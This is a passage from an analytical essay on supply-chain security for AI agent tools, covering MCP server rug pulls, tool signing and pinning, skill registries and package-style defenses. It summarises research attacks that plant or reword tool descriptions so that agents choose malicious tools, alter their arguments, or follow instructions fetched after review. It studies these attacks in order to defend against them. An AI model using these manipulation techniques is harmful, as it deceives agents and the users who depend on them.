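A signature check accepts any change the owner signs, while a pin blocks every change, including security fixes, until someone approves it. If a client also pinned the model's version and the complete list of tools, it would detect the last two changes as well. The company would then have to review the whole combination whenever it added a tool, and the model's provider would have to keep each named version unchanged.

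### Changes during use

The client has to fetch the tool list again to detect a new description. The Model Context Protocol only recommends that servers notify clients of changes, and an attacker can leave out the notice. The July 2026 specification forbids servers to vary the list between connections or as a side effect of other requests, but a malicious operator can ignore this rule. The specification still allows lists to differ according to a user's permissions, so a hash that one reviewer publishes may not match the list another user sees.

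The reuse hint that Model Context Protocol (2026) now requires in list responses offers no protection either, because the server's operator chooses the reuse period. Clients also differ in how they treat notices. In a feature request on Cursor's forum, one user complained that Cursor's command-line version ignores them until the session restarts, but that behavior would also delay a rug pull that arrived mid-session.

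Kraishan (2026), in *Same Name, Different Server*, measured how often servers in the official MCP Registry change. Of the 8,900 servers with more than one published version in August 2026, 51.1% had changed their description, packages or remote addresses. Kraishan classifies 40.6% as having changed silently, meaning they kept their identifiers while their description or destination changed. But the most common change, in 36.4% of cases, was a rewritten server description, which is a short text for the registry's listings. None of the registry's 72,606 version records contain the tool descriptions that a model reads, so the records can't be used to measure how often those descriptions change.

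The 370 servers (4.2%) that kept their name but moved their remote address to a different host are more worrying. Kraishan thinks most were routine migrations, but neither the registry nor a client can distinguish a migration from a takeover. The study also can't detect whether the program behind an unchanged address was replaced.

At least half of the servers that changed did so within a day of publication. Kraishan infers that a typical user's review describes a server that has already changed. That would apply only to users who install a server within hours of its release. Many of these early changes may also be corrections to a new listing.

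Pinning would have worked well against postmark-mcp, the best-documented real rug pull. The harmful line arrived in a new version of the package, so anyone whose lockfile specified an older version was safe until they updated.

### Signatures and meaning in one test

Badhe and Tiwari's July 2026 study includes a test framework called SkillSec-Eval. For their harmless set, they took 327 real skills from SkillsMP in 15 areas, such as database optimization and project management. They also generated attacks for each stage of a skill's life. In the admission test, they submitted malicious skills to a registry, each with one of the six faults described earlier, three structural (such as a missing signature) and three semantic (such as a deceptive description).

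Badhe and Tiwari compared three ways of checking the submissions. The first used rules to verify signatures, hashes and version order, check permissions and search for dangerous code patterns. The second used a language model to judge whether the description, permissions and instructions were consistent with each other. The third combined the two, sending the model only the submissions that had passed the rules.

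| Check | Malicious skills admitted | Harmless skills rejected |
|---|---|---|
| rules only | 52.9% | 0.0% |
| model only | 42.9% | 20.0% |
| both | 7.9% | 20.0% |

If the two checks missed skills independently, about 0.529 × 0.429 = 23% of the malicious skills would have passed both. Only 7.9% did, so the checks must mostly miss different skills. The model's prompt explains part of this. It contains the skill's description, permissions and instructions, but no signature or version history, so the model can't detect that a skill is unsigned or out of date. The rules can't detect a dishonest description in a correctly signed skill. An attacker can also reword a description until a model accepts it, but this doesn't work against a signature check.

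The study doesn't state how many skills these percentages are based on. The smallest sample that fits all three percentages is 140 malicious skills, of which the rules would have admitted 74, the model 60 and the combination 11. At that sample size, the combined check's true admission rate could be from about 4% to 14%. The ten-point difference between the rules and the model could be due to chance, but the drop to 7.9% when they are combined is too large for that.

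The 20.0% false positive rate is harder to interpret because Badhe and Tiwari can't have tested all 327 harmless skills. No whole number of rejections out of 327 rounds to 20.0%. If they tested only 20 skills and rejected four, the true rate could be anywhere from 8% to 42%. Even if it is exactly 20%, a registry of ClawHub's size would wrongly reject over 13,000 skills.

The results also depend on the mix of attacks. Someone who opens an account and signs their own malicious skill automatically avoids two of the three structural faults (a missing signature and a file altered after signing). If most attackers did this, the rules would contribute far less than they did in the test.

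### Checking updates

Badhe and Tiwari also tested having a registry treat every update as a new submission. Their system used rules to check the publisher and any new dependencies. It then converted the old and new instructions into vectors, lists of numbers that represent their meaning, and flagged the update if the two were far apart. It caught 92.5% of the malicious updates but also rejected 37% of the harmless ones.

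Both kinds of error come from using distance as a stand-in for harm. An honest author who reorganizes a skill can move its vector a long way, while an attacker who adds one well-chosen instruction may barely move it. A hash comparison detects every change, but someone then has to judge each one.

### SkillFortify

Bhardwaj's SkillFortify is designed to store the results of such judgments with the hashes. Its lockfile also records each skill's version constraints, trust score and the outcome of an automatic analysis. A solver picks a set of versions that satisfies all the constraints, including limits on what each skill may access. Bhardwaj reports that this takes a median of 27 milliseconds for a network of 1,000 skills.

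The bill of materials is most useful after an incident. If a skill turns out to be malicious, a company can look up which of its agents depend on it.

The trust score combines evidence about a skill's provenance, behavior, community and history. Scores multiply along a chain of dependencies, so a skill that scores 0.9 by itself but relies on one that scores 0.8 gets about 0.72. The score decays if nobody maintains the skill, and more good evidence never lowers it.

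These rules seem reasonable, but a patient attacker can satisfy them. The postmark-mcp package would have gathered good evidence through all its honest versions and had its best score just before the theft began. Popularity may not be worth much as evidence either. Kraishan found no correlation between an MCP server's GitHub stars and the number of weaknesses in its code. Servers with silent changes had about three times the odds of a serious weakness, so frequent updates aren't necessarily a good sign. (These were mostly signs of carelessness, and malicious servers may differ.)

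SkillFortify's lockfile has fields for signatures, but Bhardwaj leaves signing itself to a second version. The published scores from his test on 270 malicious and 270 harmless skills imply that SkillFortify caught 250 of the malicious ones and raised no false alarms. But a lockfile would preserve any mistake in the analysis, such as SkillFortify's mistaken verdict that the PowerPoint skill is harmless.

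### What MCP and its registry require

As of late 2026, the Model Context Protocol (MCP) specification doesn't require servers to sign or hash their tool descriptions, or clients to ask for approval again when a description changes. No title on the protocol's list of accepted and final proposals mentions signing, hashing or pinning tool definitions.

The official registry is somewhat stricter. According to Model Context Protocol, publishers must prove that they control the GitHub account or domain in a server's name. Model Context Protocol's *Versioning Published MCP Servers* requires a unique version string for every publication and bans ranges like the caret in the temp-convert example. How much this helps depends on the kind of server. Model Context Protocol's *MCP Registry Supported Package Types* requires a hash only for MCPB files, which bundle a local server into a single download.

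| Kind of server | What the registry entry specifies | What can still change |
|---|---|---|
| npm, PyPI or NuGet package | name and exact version | the package's own dependencies |
| Docker image | a tag or a hash | the image, if the entry uses a tag |
| MCPB file | download address and SHA-256 hash | nothing, if the client checks the hash |
| remote server | web address | the whole program |

The registry doesn't verify the MCPB hash and leaves that to the client. A remote server's operator should match the version number to the version of the service, but there is no file to check it against.

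### Proposals for signed and pinned tools

*ETDI* (Enhanced Tool Definition Interface, 2025) proposes that providers sign each tool's name, description, parameters, version and list of permissions, and that clients verify the signature. According to *Systematization of Knowledge* (2025), a survey of MCP security, any functional change would then need a new signature and the user's explicit approval.

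*ETDI* claims too much when it presents signatures as a defense against tool poisoning in general. Signatures would stop someone from impersonating a trusted provider or altering a description on its way to the user. But someone who wrote a poisoned adding tool like Invariant Labs' could sign its description too. The new approval is more valuable because it would expose the first of Friday's changes. It wouldn't expose a new program on a remote server unless the operator chose to declare it.

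*MCPS* (Sharif, 2026) proposes signing individual messages as well as tool definitions. Signing messages would also stop an intermediary from altering a tool's results unnoticed. It is an Internet-Draft, which anyone can submit to the Internet Engineering Task Force, and has no official status as a standard.

A simpler proposal, SEP-1766, would have servers publish a SHA-256 hash of every tool. MCP Hangar's *ADR-004* (2026) describes it as still open on May 1, and it doesn't appear on the list of accepted and final proposals. MCP has adopted a similar idea for skills. Its Skills Extension, which is final, lets servers deliver skills to clients. According to the company Arcade, the server declares a hash and a size for each file unless it generates the skill dynamically.

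A hash from the same server as the file protects mainly against damaged downloads, because an operator who changes the file can change the hash to match. The client can detect the change only if it has kept the old hash. Even then, Assay's developers warn that a hash doesn't make a tool safe or approved. Assay records tool hashes alongside agents' decisions so that an investigator can later establish which definition an agent was using.

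Another new MCP format, the Server Card, is a small file that describes a server before anyone connects to it. It contains no tool descriptions to sign. The format deliberately leaves out the tools because they can change while the server is running, according to *MCP Server Cards* (Nikhil Tiwari, 2026).

*Attested Tool-Server Admission* (Metere, 2026) proposes signing a statement about the server instead. An ordinary web certificate shows that a client has reached a particular address, but not that the user's organization wants tools from there. The server therefore publishes a short signed document stating how sensitive the data it handles may be. The client checks the signature against keys the organization has chosen in advance, then allows only the tools on a fixed list. Google's Gmail server publishes no such document, so the organization admits it through local configuration. The list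 might include searching and drafting emails but not deleting them. If an injected instruction tells the agent to delete every message, the client blocks the request before it reaches Google.

In Metere's own tests, the client rejected every forged document and every disguised tool name, as expected, since it compares them exactly. But the signed document contains no tool descriptions, and Metere concedes that the scheme doesn't stop an admitted server from misbehaving within its permitted tools. The scheme would have stopped the translation service from adding a new tool on Friday, but not from replacing the program behind `translate_text`.

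## Agents that choose their tools while they work

A hash, a signature or an organization's list of permitted tools protects a choice that somebody has already made. An agent with access to a large collection of tools makes the choice itself, often several times in one task. It starts from a request in the user's own words and looks for a tool whose description sounds suitable, whereas a package resolver only matches a name and a version range to one archive.

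### From a request to a tool

*Prompt Injection Attack to Tool Selection in LLM Agents* (Shi, Yuan and colleagues, 2025) divides this process into two steps, retrieval and selection. Ordinary software first retrieves a shortlist, because a model can't read about every tool in a big registry. At about 100 tokens each, the descriptions of 10,000 skills would take up a million tokens.

To do this, it uses an embedding model, which turns each text into a vector, a list of numbers. Texts with similar meanings get vectors that point in similar directions. The software compares the vector q of the user's request with the vector d of each tool description by their cosine similarity:

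cos(q, d) = (q · d) / (|q| |d|)

The result is 1 if the vectors point the same way and 0 if they are at right angles. Real embedding models use hundreds of numbers per text, but suppose they used only two, and the request "What is 86 degrees in Celsius?" became (0.8, 0.6). If a temperature converter's description became (0.6, 0.8), its similarity to the request would be 0.8 × 0.6 + 0.6 × 0.8 = 0.96. An email tool's description at (0.6, −0.8) would score 0.8 × 0.6 − 0.6 × 0.8 = 0. The denominator is 1 in both cases because all three vectors have length 1.

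The software passes the highest-scoring tools, often five, to the language model. In the selection step, the model reads their names and descriptions and picks one. An agent with only a few dozen tools can skip retrieval and show the model all of them. Neither retrieval nor selection involves running a tool or checking that it does what its description says.

ToolHijacker, an attack by Shi and colleagues, was an early demonstration that one planted description can get a tool both shortlisted and chosen. They tested it on two benchmarks, each with seven tasks and 100 wordings per task. With GPT-4o as its model, the agent chose the planted tool 96.4% of the time on one benchmark and 85.1% on the other. The second benchmark had 9,650 genuine tools, and the planted one still made the shortlist of five in at least 95% of cases.

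A tool description needs different text for retrieval than for selection. ToolHijacker's descriptions have one part for each step, and Shi and colleagues tested the parts separately on one task. With only the retrieval part, the tool always made the shortlist, but the model chose it 5% of the time. With only the selection part, the tool made the shortlist 65% of the time, and the model chose it in nearly all of those cases. Fixing a registry's search engine therefore doesn't stop the model from choosing a malicious tool that still reaches the shortlist.

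### Getting onto the shortlist

Saha and colleagues tested retrieval with 100 skills from ClawHub, 20 in each of five categories such as email and travel. They added about 20 tokens to each SKILL.md, roughly 1% of an average file. A search program chose the tokens to bring the file's vector closer to that of a one-word query such as "travel". The added text raised the skill's retrieval score in 86% of pairs, by an average of 16.4%. The modified skill ranked in the top three of its category 56% of the time and in the top ten 80% of the time, compared with 15% and 50% for an average skill among 20.

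The 86% applies to one embedding model from OpenAI, and only to text tuned on that same model. With two open models from the Beijing Academy of Artificial Intelligence, the same method raised the score only 53% and 45% of the time. Text tuned on one of these open models still raised the OpenAI score in about 80% of pairs, but by little more than 1%. The modified skills reached the top ten only about half the time, as they would have by chance. So an attacker needs to be able to query the model that a registry uses to gain much from this method. In the paper's examples, the added words don't form sentences, so anyone who read to the end of the file would probably notice them.

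Registries can also take popularity into account. Saha and colleagues modeled a ranking score on ClawHub's:

S = S_lex + S_vec + 0.08 · log(1 + downloads)

The first two terms measure how closely the skill's wording and meaning match the query. The paper doesn't give the base of the logarithm. With base 10, a skill with ten times as many downloads as its rival gets an extra 0.08. With the natural logarithm, it gets an extra 0.08 × ln 10 ≈ 0.18, and a skill's first ten downloads add 0.19, slightly more than going from 1,000 downloads to 10,000.

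Whether the 0.18 from a tenfold lead in downloads is enough to protect a popular skill depends on the similarity scores, but Saha and colleagues report the attack's gains only in relative terms. If a skill started with a similarity of 0.4, a 16.4% increase would add about 0.07, as much as having 2.3 times the downloads. A tenfold lead would outweigh that, but few skills have one over all their rivals. When the researchers gave the modified skills 579 downloads, the average on ClawHub, these skills beat the baseline 74% of the time. A typical skill in their collection had about 850 downloads, which would put it only 0.03 ahead of a skill with 579. The most popular email skill, with 41,665 downloads, would be 0.34 ahead.

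Newly published skills have no such protection. At launch, modified skills with zero downloads won 94% of the time against other new skills. An hour later, when the other skills had started to collect downloads, the modified skills won 40% of the time. The popularity term therefore does help, but its effect comes from the first few downloads, which are the easiest for an attacker to fake if the registry doesn't check them.

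An attacker can also publish many copies of a malicious skill. Badhe and Tiwari tested this in SkillSec-Eval by adding malicious skills to their repository and running 440 queries. With 15 near-identical copies of a malicious skill, at least one made the shortlist of five for 93.2% of the queries, and the copies took an average of 2.84 of the five places. They then added a filter that removed near-duplicates and skills whose instructions or permissions didn't fit their descriptions, which cut the 93.2% figure to 26.6%.

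They also report that stuffing a description with keywords got a malicious skill onto 46.6% of the shortlists and that a more natural disguise got one onto 61.1%. These figures conflict with the paper's averages of 0.38 and 0.42 malicious skills per shortlist. If 61.1% of the shortlists contain at least one malicious skill, the average can't be below 0.61. The result for copies doesn't have this problem.

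### Persuading the model

Once a tool is on the shortlist, rewording its name and description can make an agent more likely to choose it. In *ToolTweak*, Sneh, Yan and colleagues (2025) gave agents five tools that could do the same job, so an agent with no preference would send each about 20% of the requests. A language model then rewrote the name and description of one tool up to ten times, guided by how often the agent had picked it. The tool's share rose to 81.6% with DeepSeek, the most affected of the six models tested, and to 34.0% with Llama 3.1, the least affected.

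Rewriting the descriptions was mostly unnecessary. A fixed passage that praised the tool, urged agents to use it and claimed a large following did better than the rewritten descriptions on five of the six models, and reached 89.5% with Grok 3 Mini. Names also affected the choice. In one comparison, agents chose two identical tools at very different rates when the names differed only in a final "1" or "2".

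The attacker in *ToolTweak* can be a legitimate company with a tool that works. Sneh and colleagues compare the attack to search engine optimization and note that providers who charge per call would earn more by using it. An honest provider could test two wordings, keep the one that agents prefer and see nothing wrong with that. If enough providers do this, agents will tend to pick the best-advertised tools even when nobody is distributing malware.

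Saha and colleagues found a similar effect in skills. They gave an agent two functionally identical skills, one of which had an extra sentence in its description. The sentence praised the skill, told the agent to choose it, or claimed it was up to date or secure. In 2,000 trials with each of four models, the agents chose the skill with the extra sentence 77.6% of the time on average, compared with the 50% expected if the sentence had no effect. Sentences that praised the skill or told the agent to choose it had the largest effect.

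The altered skill's name and position may explain part of this effect. In the paper's examples, its name also ends in "-pro", although the researchers say they changed only the description. In the one trial they print, the altered skill is also first in the list, and Sneh and colleagues found that one model strongly preferred whichever tool came first. The suffix and position are unlikely to explain the whole gap, since different sentences had different effects. But a control with the same name and order and no added sentence would have shown how much of the 77.6% is due to persuasion.

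Badhe and Tiwari tried several kinds of deception in their selection test. The model received a request and a shortlist of five skills, one of them malicious, and had to choose using only the descriptions and declared permissions. The researchers then repeated the test with a validation step that cleaned up the descriptions and compared them with what the skills did.

| What the malicious skill's description contained | Chosen without validation | Chosen with validation |
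|---|---|---|
| a false endorsement, such as "official" | 45.64% | 8.72% |
| a false claim of safe behavior, such as working only locally | 27.27% | 0.00% |
| an incomplete list of permissions | 11.36% | 5.68% |
| an ordinary description | 9.88% | 2.47% |
| an overt prompt injection | 4.69% | 3.65% |

The false endorsement succeeded almost ten times as often as the overt injection. The injection may have done worse than an ordinary description, perhaps because the model detected the manipulation, but the samples are too small to be sure. The injection percentages fit 9 choices out of 192 without validation and 7 with it, so the slight improvement with validation could also be due to chance.

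The paper is also unclear about which model made the choices. Its setup description names Gemini 3.1 Pro, but its results section names Gemini 1.5 Flash, a much older and smaller model. If the results come from Gemini 1.5 Flash, they are weak evidence of how current models respond to endorsements.

Even so, the test illustrates a weakness in any defense that looks for commands. A statement that a skill is official contains no instruction for a filter to detect. The model can't simply ignore such statements either, because it has to choose a skill based on the claims in its description. Shi and colleagues' results fit this explanation. They tried ToolHijacker on two models that other researchers had trained to ignore instructions in data, and on one benchmark the attack still succeeded 99.7% and 96.7% of the time.

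Saha and colleagues saw the same pattern when they tried to get malicious skills past a copy of ClawHub's review process. The process blocked about 68% of skills with a plainly worded malicious instruction, and 63.5% when the skills also contained an appeal to the reviewing model to approve them. When the researchers reworded the malicious instruction as routine procedure, the process blocked only 26%.

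A defender can rewrite all the tool descriptions in a neutral style before the model sees them. In Sneh and colleagues' test, this reduced the share of selections going to tools with the fixed passage of praise to between 20% and 38%, compared with the 20% expected without any advantage. Tools optimized by *ToolTweak* still received between 27% and 63%. The rewriting didn't change their names, which may explain some of the difference. It also couldn't remove an advantage that came from false factual claims rather than tone.

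Claims in a skill's description need to be checked against something outside it. Badhe and Tiwari's validation step eliminated false claims of safe behavior because it could compare them with the skill's instructions. Endorsements are harder to check because nothing in the skill shows whether they are genuine. The validation step removed endorsements, so a skill that really is official would lose its label too. A registry that verifies publishers could put their status in a separate field that skill authors can't edit.

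### Better disguises and altered arguments

Dai, Sun and Tao (2026), in *Spoofing the Toolbox*, report an attack that uses persuasive but inconspicuous tool descriptions. With ten tools available, it succeeded up to 92.1% of the time against GPT-5. With 20 tools, it succeeded about 80% of the time against the model used to develop the descriptions. The five detectors in the main test flagged at most 4.25% of the descriptions.

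People did no better at telling the optimized description from the genuine one. Participants ranked six descriptions of a tool from most suspicious (1) to least suspicious (6). The genuine description got an average rank of 4.03, the optimized one 4.00, and ToolHijacker's 2.68. Some client applications show the user a tool's description before running it, which would help against crude attacks such as ToolHijacker's but offer little protection against these newer ones.

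An attacker can also change what the agent asks a tool to do without changing which tool it chooses. In *Subverting Tool Arguments*, Dai, Sun and colleagues (2026) altered descriptions so that an agent would fill in one argument, such as a file path, with the attacker's value instead of the user's. This is possible because the model writes the arguments with all the descriptions in its context, as the notation of Birhan and colleagues shows. On three benchmarks, the attack both worked and got past five detectors in 93.8%, 81.5% and 63.8% of cases, averaged over six models.

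The highest figure seems to rest on only 16 tasks, and the paper's text gives it as 95.3% instead. The lowest comes from the benchmark in which users state the value themselves, for example by naming the file to read. Users can therefore reduce the risk by being specific, but most people use an agent partly to avoid spelling out such details. The tool's description has to convey the attacker's value somehow, so a reviewer who finds a particular path or address in a general-purpose tool's description should ask why it is there.

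### Harmless tools that combine badly

A reviewer can read a lockfile before the program runs. When an agent searches a registry for tools, the list of tools it used exists only after the task is finished, and the next request or a change in the registry's ranking may produce a different list. Badhe and Tiwari add that an updated skill may go into use without anyone reviewing the new version.

Reviewing each tool separately isn't enough either. Suppose one skill summarizes customer complaints, another posts updates to a company's public status page, and both work exactly as described. If a user asks the agent to explain yesterday's outage to customers, the agent might gather information with the first skill and publish it with the second, putting a customer's name and account number on a public page.

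Packages can also combine harmfully, as when a program reads a private file with one library and uploads it with another. But a programmer wrote the code that passes the data between them, and a colleague can read it. In an agent, the model makes that connection during the task, so a reviewer can't read it beforehand. The number of possible combinations also grows quickly. With forty tools, a patient team could check all 780 pairs, but there are 59,280 ordered sequences of three different tools.

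Badhe and Tiwari tested such attacks, along with unauthorized tool calls and forbidden data transfers. Without protection, every attack succeeded. They then added a monitor that labels sensitive data when a tool returns it and checks every later call before it runs. The monitor blocks any call that would send labeled data to an untrusted destination. With the monitor, 23% of the attacks still succeeded.

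Many of the failures happened because the monitor recognizes sensitive data by its exact wording, so it loses track of the data when the model paraphrases or summarizes. It tracked data correctly in 66.67% of cases, but the paper doesn't give the number of cases, which could be as few as three. A stricter monitor could treat everything the model writes after reading a secret as secret. This would catch the paraphrases, but it would also stop an agent from emailing a harmless summary of a confidential report, even if that is what the user wants.

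### People also choose by description and popularity

A skeptic could reply that developers don't choose packages any more carefully than agents do. Most search for a few words, look at the README and the download count, and install whatever seems popular. Few read the code. Typosquatting works because people make careless choices, and search engine optimization worked on people long before anyone tried it on agents. An agent might even choose better, since it can compare 20 descriptions, which most people would find tedious.

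This is a fair description of how many developers behave, so persuasion is not a new problem. The main difference is that a developer chooses a package once, and the project file and lockfile record the choice. Colleagues can then question it, a scanner can check it every night, and the company can find every project that uses the package if it turns out to be malicious. All of this is possible even if the developer chose carelessly.

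An agent chooses again for every task, and the user often doesn't see the choice. Small chances add up under these conditions. In SkillSec-Eval, the falsely endorsed skill still won 8.7% of selections after validation. If an agent faced that risk independently in each task, the probability that it would choose the malicious skill at least once in 20 tasks would be 84%. (This assumes that the skill makes the shortlist every time.)

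Packages are riskier in one way, because a program runs a malicious package every time it starts, while an agent that picks a malicious skill today may pick a good one tomorrow. But each new choice gives attackers another chance, and one theft of credentials is usually enough, so repeated chances probably matter more than repeated use. A log of every tool the agent used would help a company investigate afterwards, but it wouldn't let anyone review the tools before they run, as a lockfile does for packages.

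### What a fixed list restores and costs

An organization can regain much of that opportunity for review by giving its agents a fixed list of approved tools. Someone can then read each description, pin each file and at least consider the riskier pairs of tools. An unapproved tool can't reach the agent's shortlist, even if its author tunes the text or publishes 15 copies. If the approved list is short enough, the agent doesn't need retrieval.

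A list works best if it contains only one tool for each job. Every selection attack described above makes the agent prefer one tool over another that would do as well, so an agent with only one email tool gives attackers very little choice to influence. The drawback is that the agent has no substitute when that tool is down or handles a request badly.

Even with a fixed list of tools, the model decides when to call each one and what arguments to give it, so a poisoned description that got past the reviewer could lead it to redirect a payment or an email. A remote server can also change while its entry on the list stays the same, and two non-malicious tools can together leak data.

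The most obvious drawback of a fixed list is that the agent can't do anything the approved tools don't cover. If a user needs to convert an unusual file format and no approved tool can do it, the agent has to give up or ask. Users who often run into this may connect an unapproved tool themselves or switch to an unrestricted agent. None of these studies measures how many tasks a fixed list would rule out. The loss is probably small for an agent that only answers billing questions and large for a general assistant.

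Somebody also has to maintain the list and may be tempted to keep adding to it. In *Spoofing the Toolbox*, models chose the right tool 81.7% of the time with 10 tools and 62.5% of the time with 40, without any attack. An organization that has approved 40 tools could therefore do better to give each agent only the ten or so that its job requires. That would also cut the number of pairs of tools from 780 to 45.

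A compromise is to let the agent search a registry and suggest a tool, but not use it until a person has added it to the list of allowed tools. The agent can still search the whole registry, though it has to wait for approval, and each choice leaves a record. The person needs more than the tool's description to judge it, since Dai, Sun and Tao's participants couldn't tell optimized descriptions from genuine ones.

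## Which package defenses carry over and what must be added

Anyone who maintains a list of approved agent tools can use the checks that developers already apply to packages. But each check rests on an assumption about packages, and some of these assumptions fit agent tools badly.

| Defense | What it assumes about packages | Does this hold for agent tools? | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| publisher identity and namespaces | a registry can find out who controls a name | yes, if the registry checks | carries over |
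| curated collections | reviewers see what users will get | yes, unless the tool runs remotely or fetches its instructions | carries over, with a rule on outside instructions |
| waiting before adopting new versions | somebody else will find the problem first | often for malware, less often for manipulative text | carries over in part |
| version pinning | the same file behaves the same way | for code, but a text's effect also depends on the model | carries over for files |
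| takedown and revocation | users keep returning to the registry | no, because people copy skills | weakens |
| limits on file types | harm hides in files that reviewers can't read | yes for code, no for prose | carries over, but leaves text attacks alone |
| lookalike-name checks | victims mistake one name for another | people do, but agents choose mostly by description | misses most text attacks |
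| scanning | malicious files share recognizable patterns | yes for mass-produced malware | catches familiar attacks, misses new prose |
| declared permissions | the system enforces the declaration | rarely | weak until something enforces them |
| user approval | users understand what they approve | rarely | weakens |
| sandboxes | a program can do its job with limited access | yes for many tools | carries over, up to the access the job needs |

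Package defenses generally carry over to agent tools if they don't depend on what a tool's text means. Defenses that rely on a declared purpose or an attentive user are usually weaker, and those that look for known malware or similar names usually miss text attacks. Takedowns are an exception, because they don't depend on meaning but still work worse for skills than for packages. Declared permissions are another, because they become one of the better defenses once software enforces them.

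### Publisher identity

A registry can check who controls an account or a web domain without reading the upload, so identity checks work as well for agent tools as for packages. Skill marketplaces have barely tried them. Li and colleagues found no marketplace that ties publication to a verified identity. During the ClawHavoc campaign, ClawHub accepted uploads from any account more than a week old, and twelve accounts published at least 1,184 malicious skills.

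Requiring publishers to prove they control a domain would make impersonation harder and give the registry something to block, though it wouldn't stop a criminal who can buy a domain for ten dollars. The developer of postmark-mcp needed only a name that nobody had claimed on npm. Under a rule like the MCP Registry's, only someone who controlled Postmark's domain or GitHub account could have published a server under Postmark's name.

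Identity checks fail for both tools and packages when an attacker hijacks an account. Li and colleagues point out that the attacker then doesn't have to persuade anyone to install something new, because existing users receive the harmful version as a routine update.

### Curated collections

Trail of Bits prefers curated collections partly because a public scanner gives an attacker unlimited attempts. The firm needed less than an hour to devise and build three of its four malicious test skills. In a curated collection, somebody decides which sources are acceptable and who may approve a change, so each attempt must get past a person.

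That person can also use knowledge that isn't in the file. Anthropic's own skills for Office documents contain a helper script that loads a library into another program, and Trail of Bits finds it hard to imagine a skill doing anything more suspicious. The model in Cisco's scanner rated the script a low risk because it accepted the explanation in the skill, but a malicious author could write the same explanation. A curator who knows that the script comes from Anthropic has a better reason to accept it. (Even so, the script could load a harmful file that somebody else had planted, so a good author isn't a complete answer.)

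Human review can still fail when the harmful text is outside the files being reviewed. Li and colleagues describe an experiment from June 2026 in which researchers at the company Air Security submitted a skill to an open-source community repository. Its maintainers reviewed and accepted it. The researchers then advertised the skill on Instagram and gained control of more than 26,000 agents. The skill's own files were harmless, but they directed the agent to a documentation page that the researchers controlled and used to serve the payload after the review. A pinned hash would still have matched because the skill's files had not changed.

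Air Security also scanned 142,836 published skills and found that 17,822, about one in eight, send agents to outside instructions that could change at any time. A curated collection would have to reject such skills or keep its own copy of those instructions. Copies go out of date, but they let reviewers check the same text the agent will read.

Trail of Bits doesn't measure how much safer users of curated collections are, so the case for curation rests on reasoning and on the poor record of the alternatives. The reasoning is persuasive for a company that needs thirty skills, but much less so for someone who wants an agent to find the right skill among thousands.

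### Waiting before adopting a new version

Some package managers can refuse any version younger than a chosen age, such as two weeks. The delay gives other people time to find malware. A two-week delay would probably have worked against postmark-mcp, since only 11 days passed between the reported upload date and the package's entry in OSV's database. A short wait also suits MCP servers because many of them change within a day of publication, as Kraishan found.

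The delay helps only if somebody notices the problem in time. Li and colleagues report that a malicious skill on skills.sh stole developers' credentials throughout July 2026. If the harmful version was there from the start, a two-week delay would have ended while the skill was still spreading. A skill that biases an agent's advice could go unnoticed for much longer.

The delay also has to cover everything the tool loads. The company SafeDep showed why with a script that named a Python package without specifying a version. The software that ran the script installed whatever version was current, so a skill that had been public for months could bring in a package published that morning. With a remote server, users can't wait, because the operator decides when to update the program. Waiting also postpones security fixes, so a company needs a way to let urgent ones through.

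### Takedowns that don't reach the copies

When a registry deletes a malicious package, any build that fetches it again will fail, which alerts the build's owner. A skill is a folder that people copy into their own projects, so many users never return to the place where they found it.

The security company Zenity, which reported the July campaign, counted more than 1.7 million installations. The hosting platforms removed the listings and repositories within twelve hours of notification, but copies survived in other repositories, on websites that had mirrored the listing and on users' machines. Li and colleagues conclude that response time wasn't the main constraint, because the skill format has no way to alert installed copies to a problem. Earlier discovery would still have helped, since the campaign had already run for a month.

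A client could close part of this gap by checking a public list of revoked hashes whenever it loads a skill. An attacker could get around the list by changing one byte of the skill, but copies already on users' machines would still match.

Deleting a malicious skill may not be enough either, because the skill can add instructions to files such as AGENTS.md and CLAUDE.md, which coding agents read at the start of each session. Those instructions remain after the user deletes the skill.

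Revocation can work better for agent tools than for packages only when the tool runs on a remote server. If the hosting company shuts the server down, the tool stops working for every user at once. Removing the registry entry isn't enough, because anyone who already has the address can still connect.

### File types and lookalike names

ClawHub distributes only certain types of files and excludes compiled programs and archives. Trail of Bits thinks this rules out many attacks without limiting what skills can usefully do. One of its test skills contained a compiled file that differed from the readable source code beside it. The skill passed the scanners on skills.sh, which doesn't restrict file types. ClawHub's rule would have excluded the compiled file.

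The rule can't exclude text, because a skill consists of text. Trail of Bits got past both of ClawHub's scanners on its first attempt, using only permitted files. A registry could extend the rule to invisible characters. Li and colleagues cite work by Pillar Security in which such characters hid instructions from human reviewers while leaving them readable to coding assistants. Some emoji and writing systems need a few of these characters, but a registry can decide which ones to allow without judging what the text means.

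A lookalike-name check usually counts the single-letter additions, removals and changes needed to turn one name into another. The names "clawhub" and "clawhubb" are one letter apart, so the check should catch the ClawHavoc skills that misspelled the name of ClawHub's own program. It would not have flagged postmark-mcp, because npm had no genuine package for it to resemble.

Sometimes a malicious name doesn't imitate an existing one. Language models that write skills occasionally invent a package name, and Aikido Security found cases in which attackers had later registered the invented names. Most importantly, an agent that searches by meaning can pick a malicious tool whose name resembles no other, because the search mainly compares descriptions.

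### Permissions and approvals

A phone's camera permission works because the operating system blocks apps without it from using the camera. The specification for skills doesn't require similar enforcement of the `allowed-tools` field. Claude Code applies the field but Anthropic's Agent SDK does not, so a reviewer can test a skill with its restrictions in place and a company can then deploy it without them. Li and colleagues argue that this leaves users worse informed than if the skill had declared nothing.

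User approval has a similar weakness. In December 2025, researchers at Cato Networks demonstrated a skill that was described as an image-to-GIF converter but also downloaded and ran ransomware. One approval at installation covered both actions, and the model couldn't warn the user because it never saw the script's source code.

Asking users for approval more often can make them less careful. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues warn that tired or overloaded people approve unsafe actions, and Li and colleagues recall that users of early Android versions learned to accept every request. The dialog also has to appear before the actions it is meant to control. Check Point Research found that a malicious project could make Claude Code run commands before asking the user whether to trust the project, which Anthropic has since fixed.

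Approvals probably work best when they are rare and specific. A dialog that shows the full address of an unfamiliar recipient gives the user something to judge, unlike "Allow this tool?" Li and colleagues suggest asking for approval again only when an update changes a skill's behavior by more than a set amount. This would interrupt users less often, but it requires a good measure of behavior. The distance measure that Badhe and Tiwari tried rejected 37% of harmless updates.

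### Least privilege and AgentBound

None of these checks is reliable enough to keep every harmful tool out, so it matters what an agent can do after a tool has misled it. The basic precaution is least privilege, which *A Formal Security Framework for MCP-Based AI Agents* (2026) expresses as an intersection of two sets. If G is what the agent may do and D is what a tool declares that it needs, the permissions E in effect while the agent uses the tool must satisfy

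E ⊆ G ∩ D

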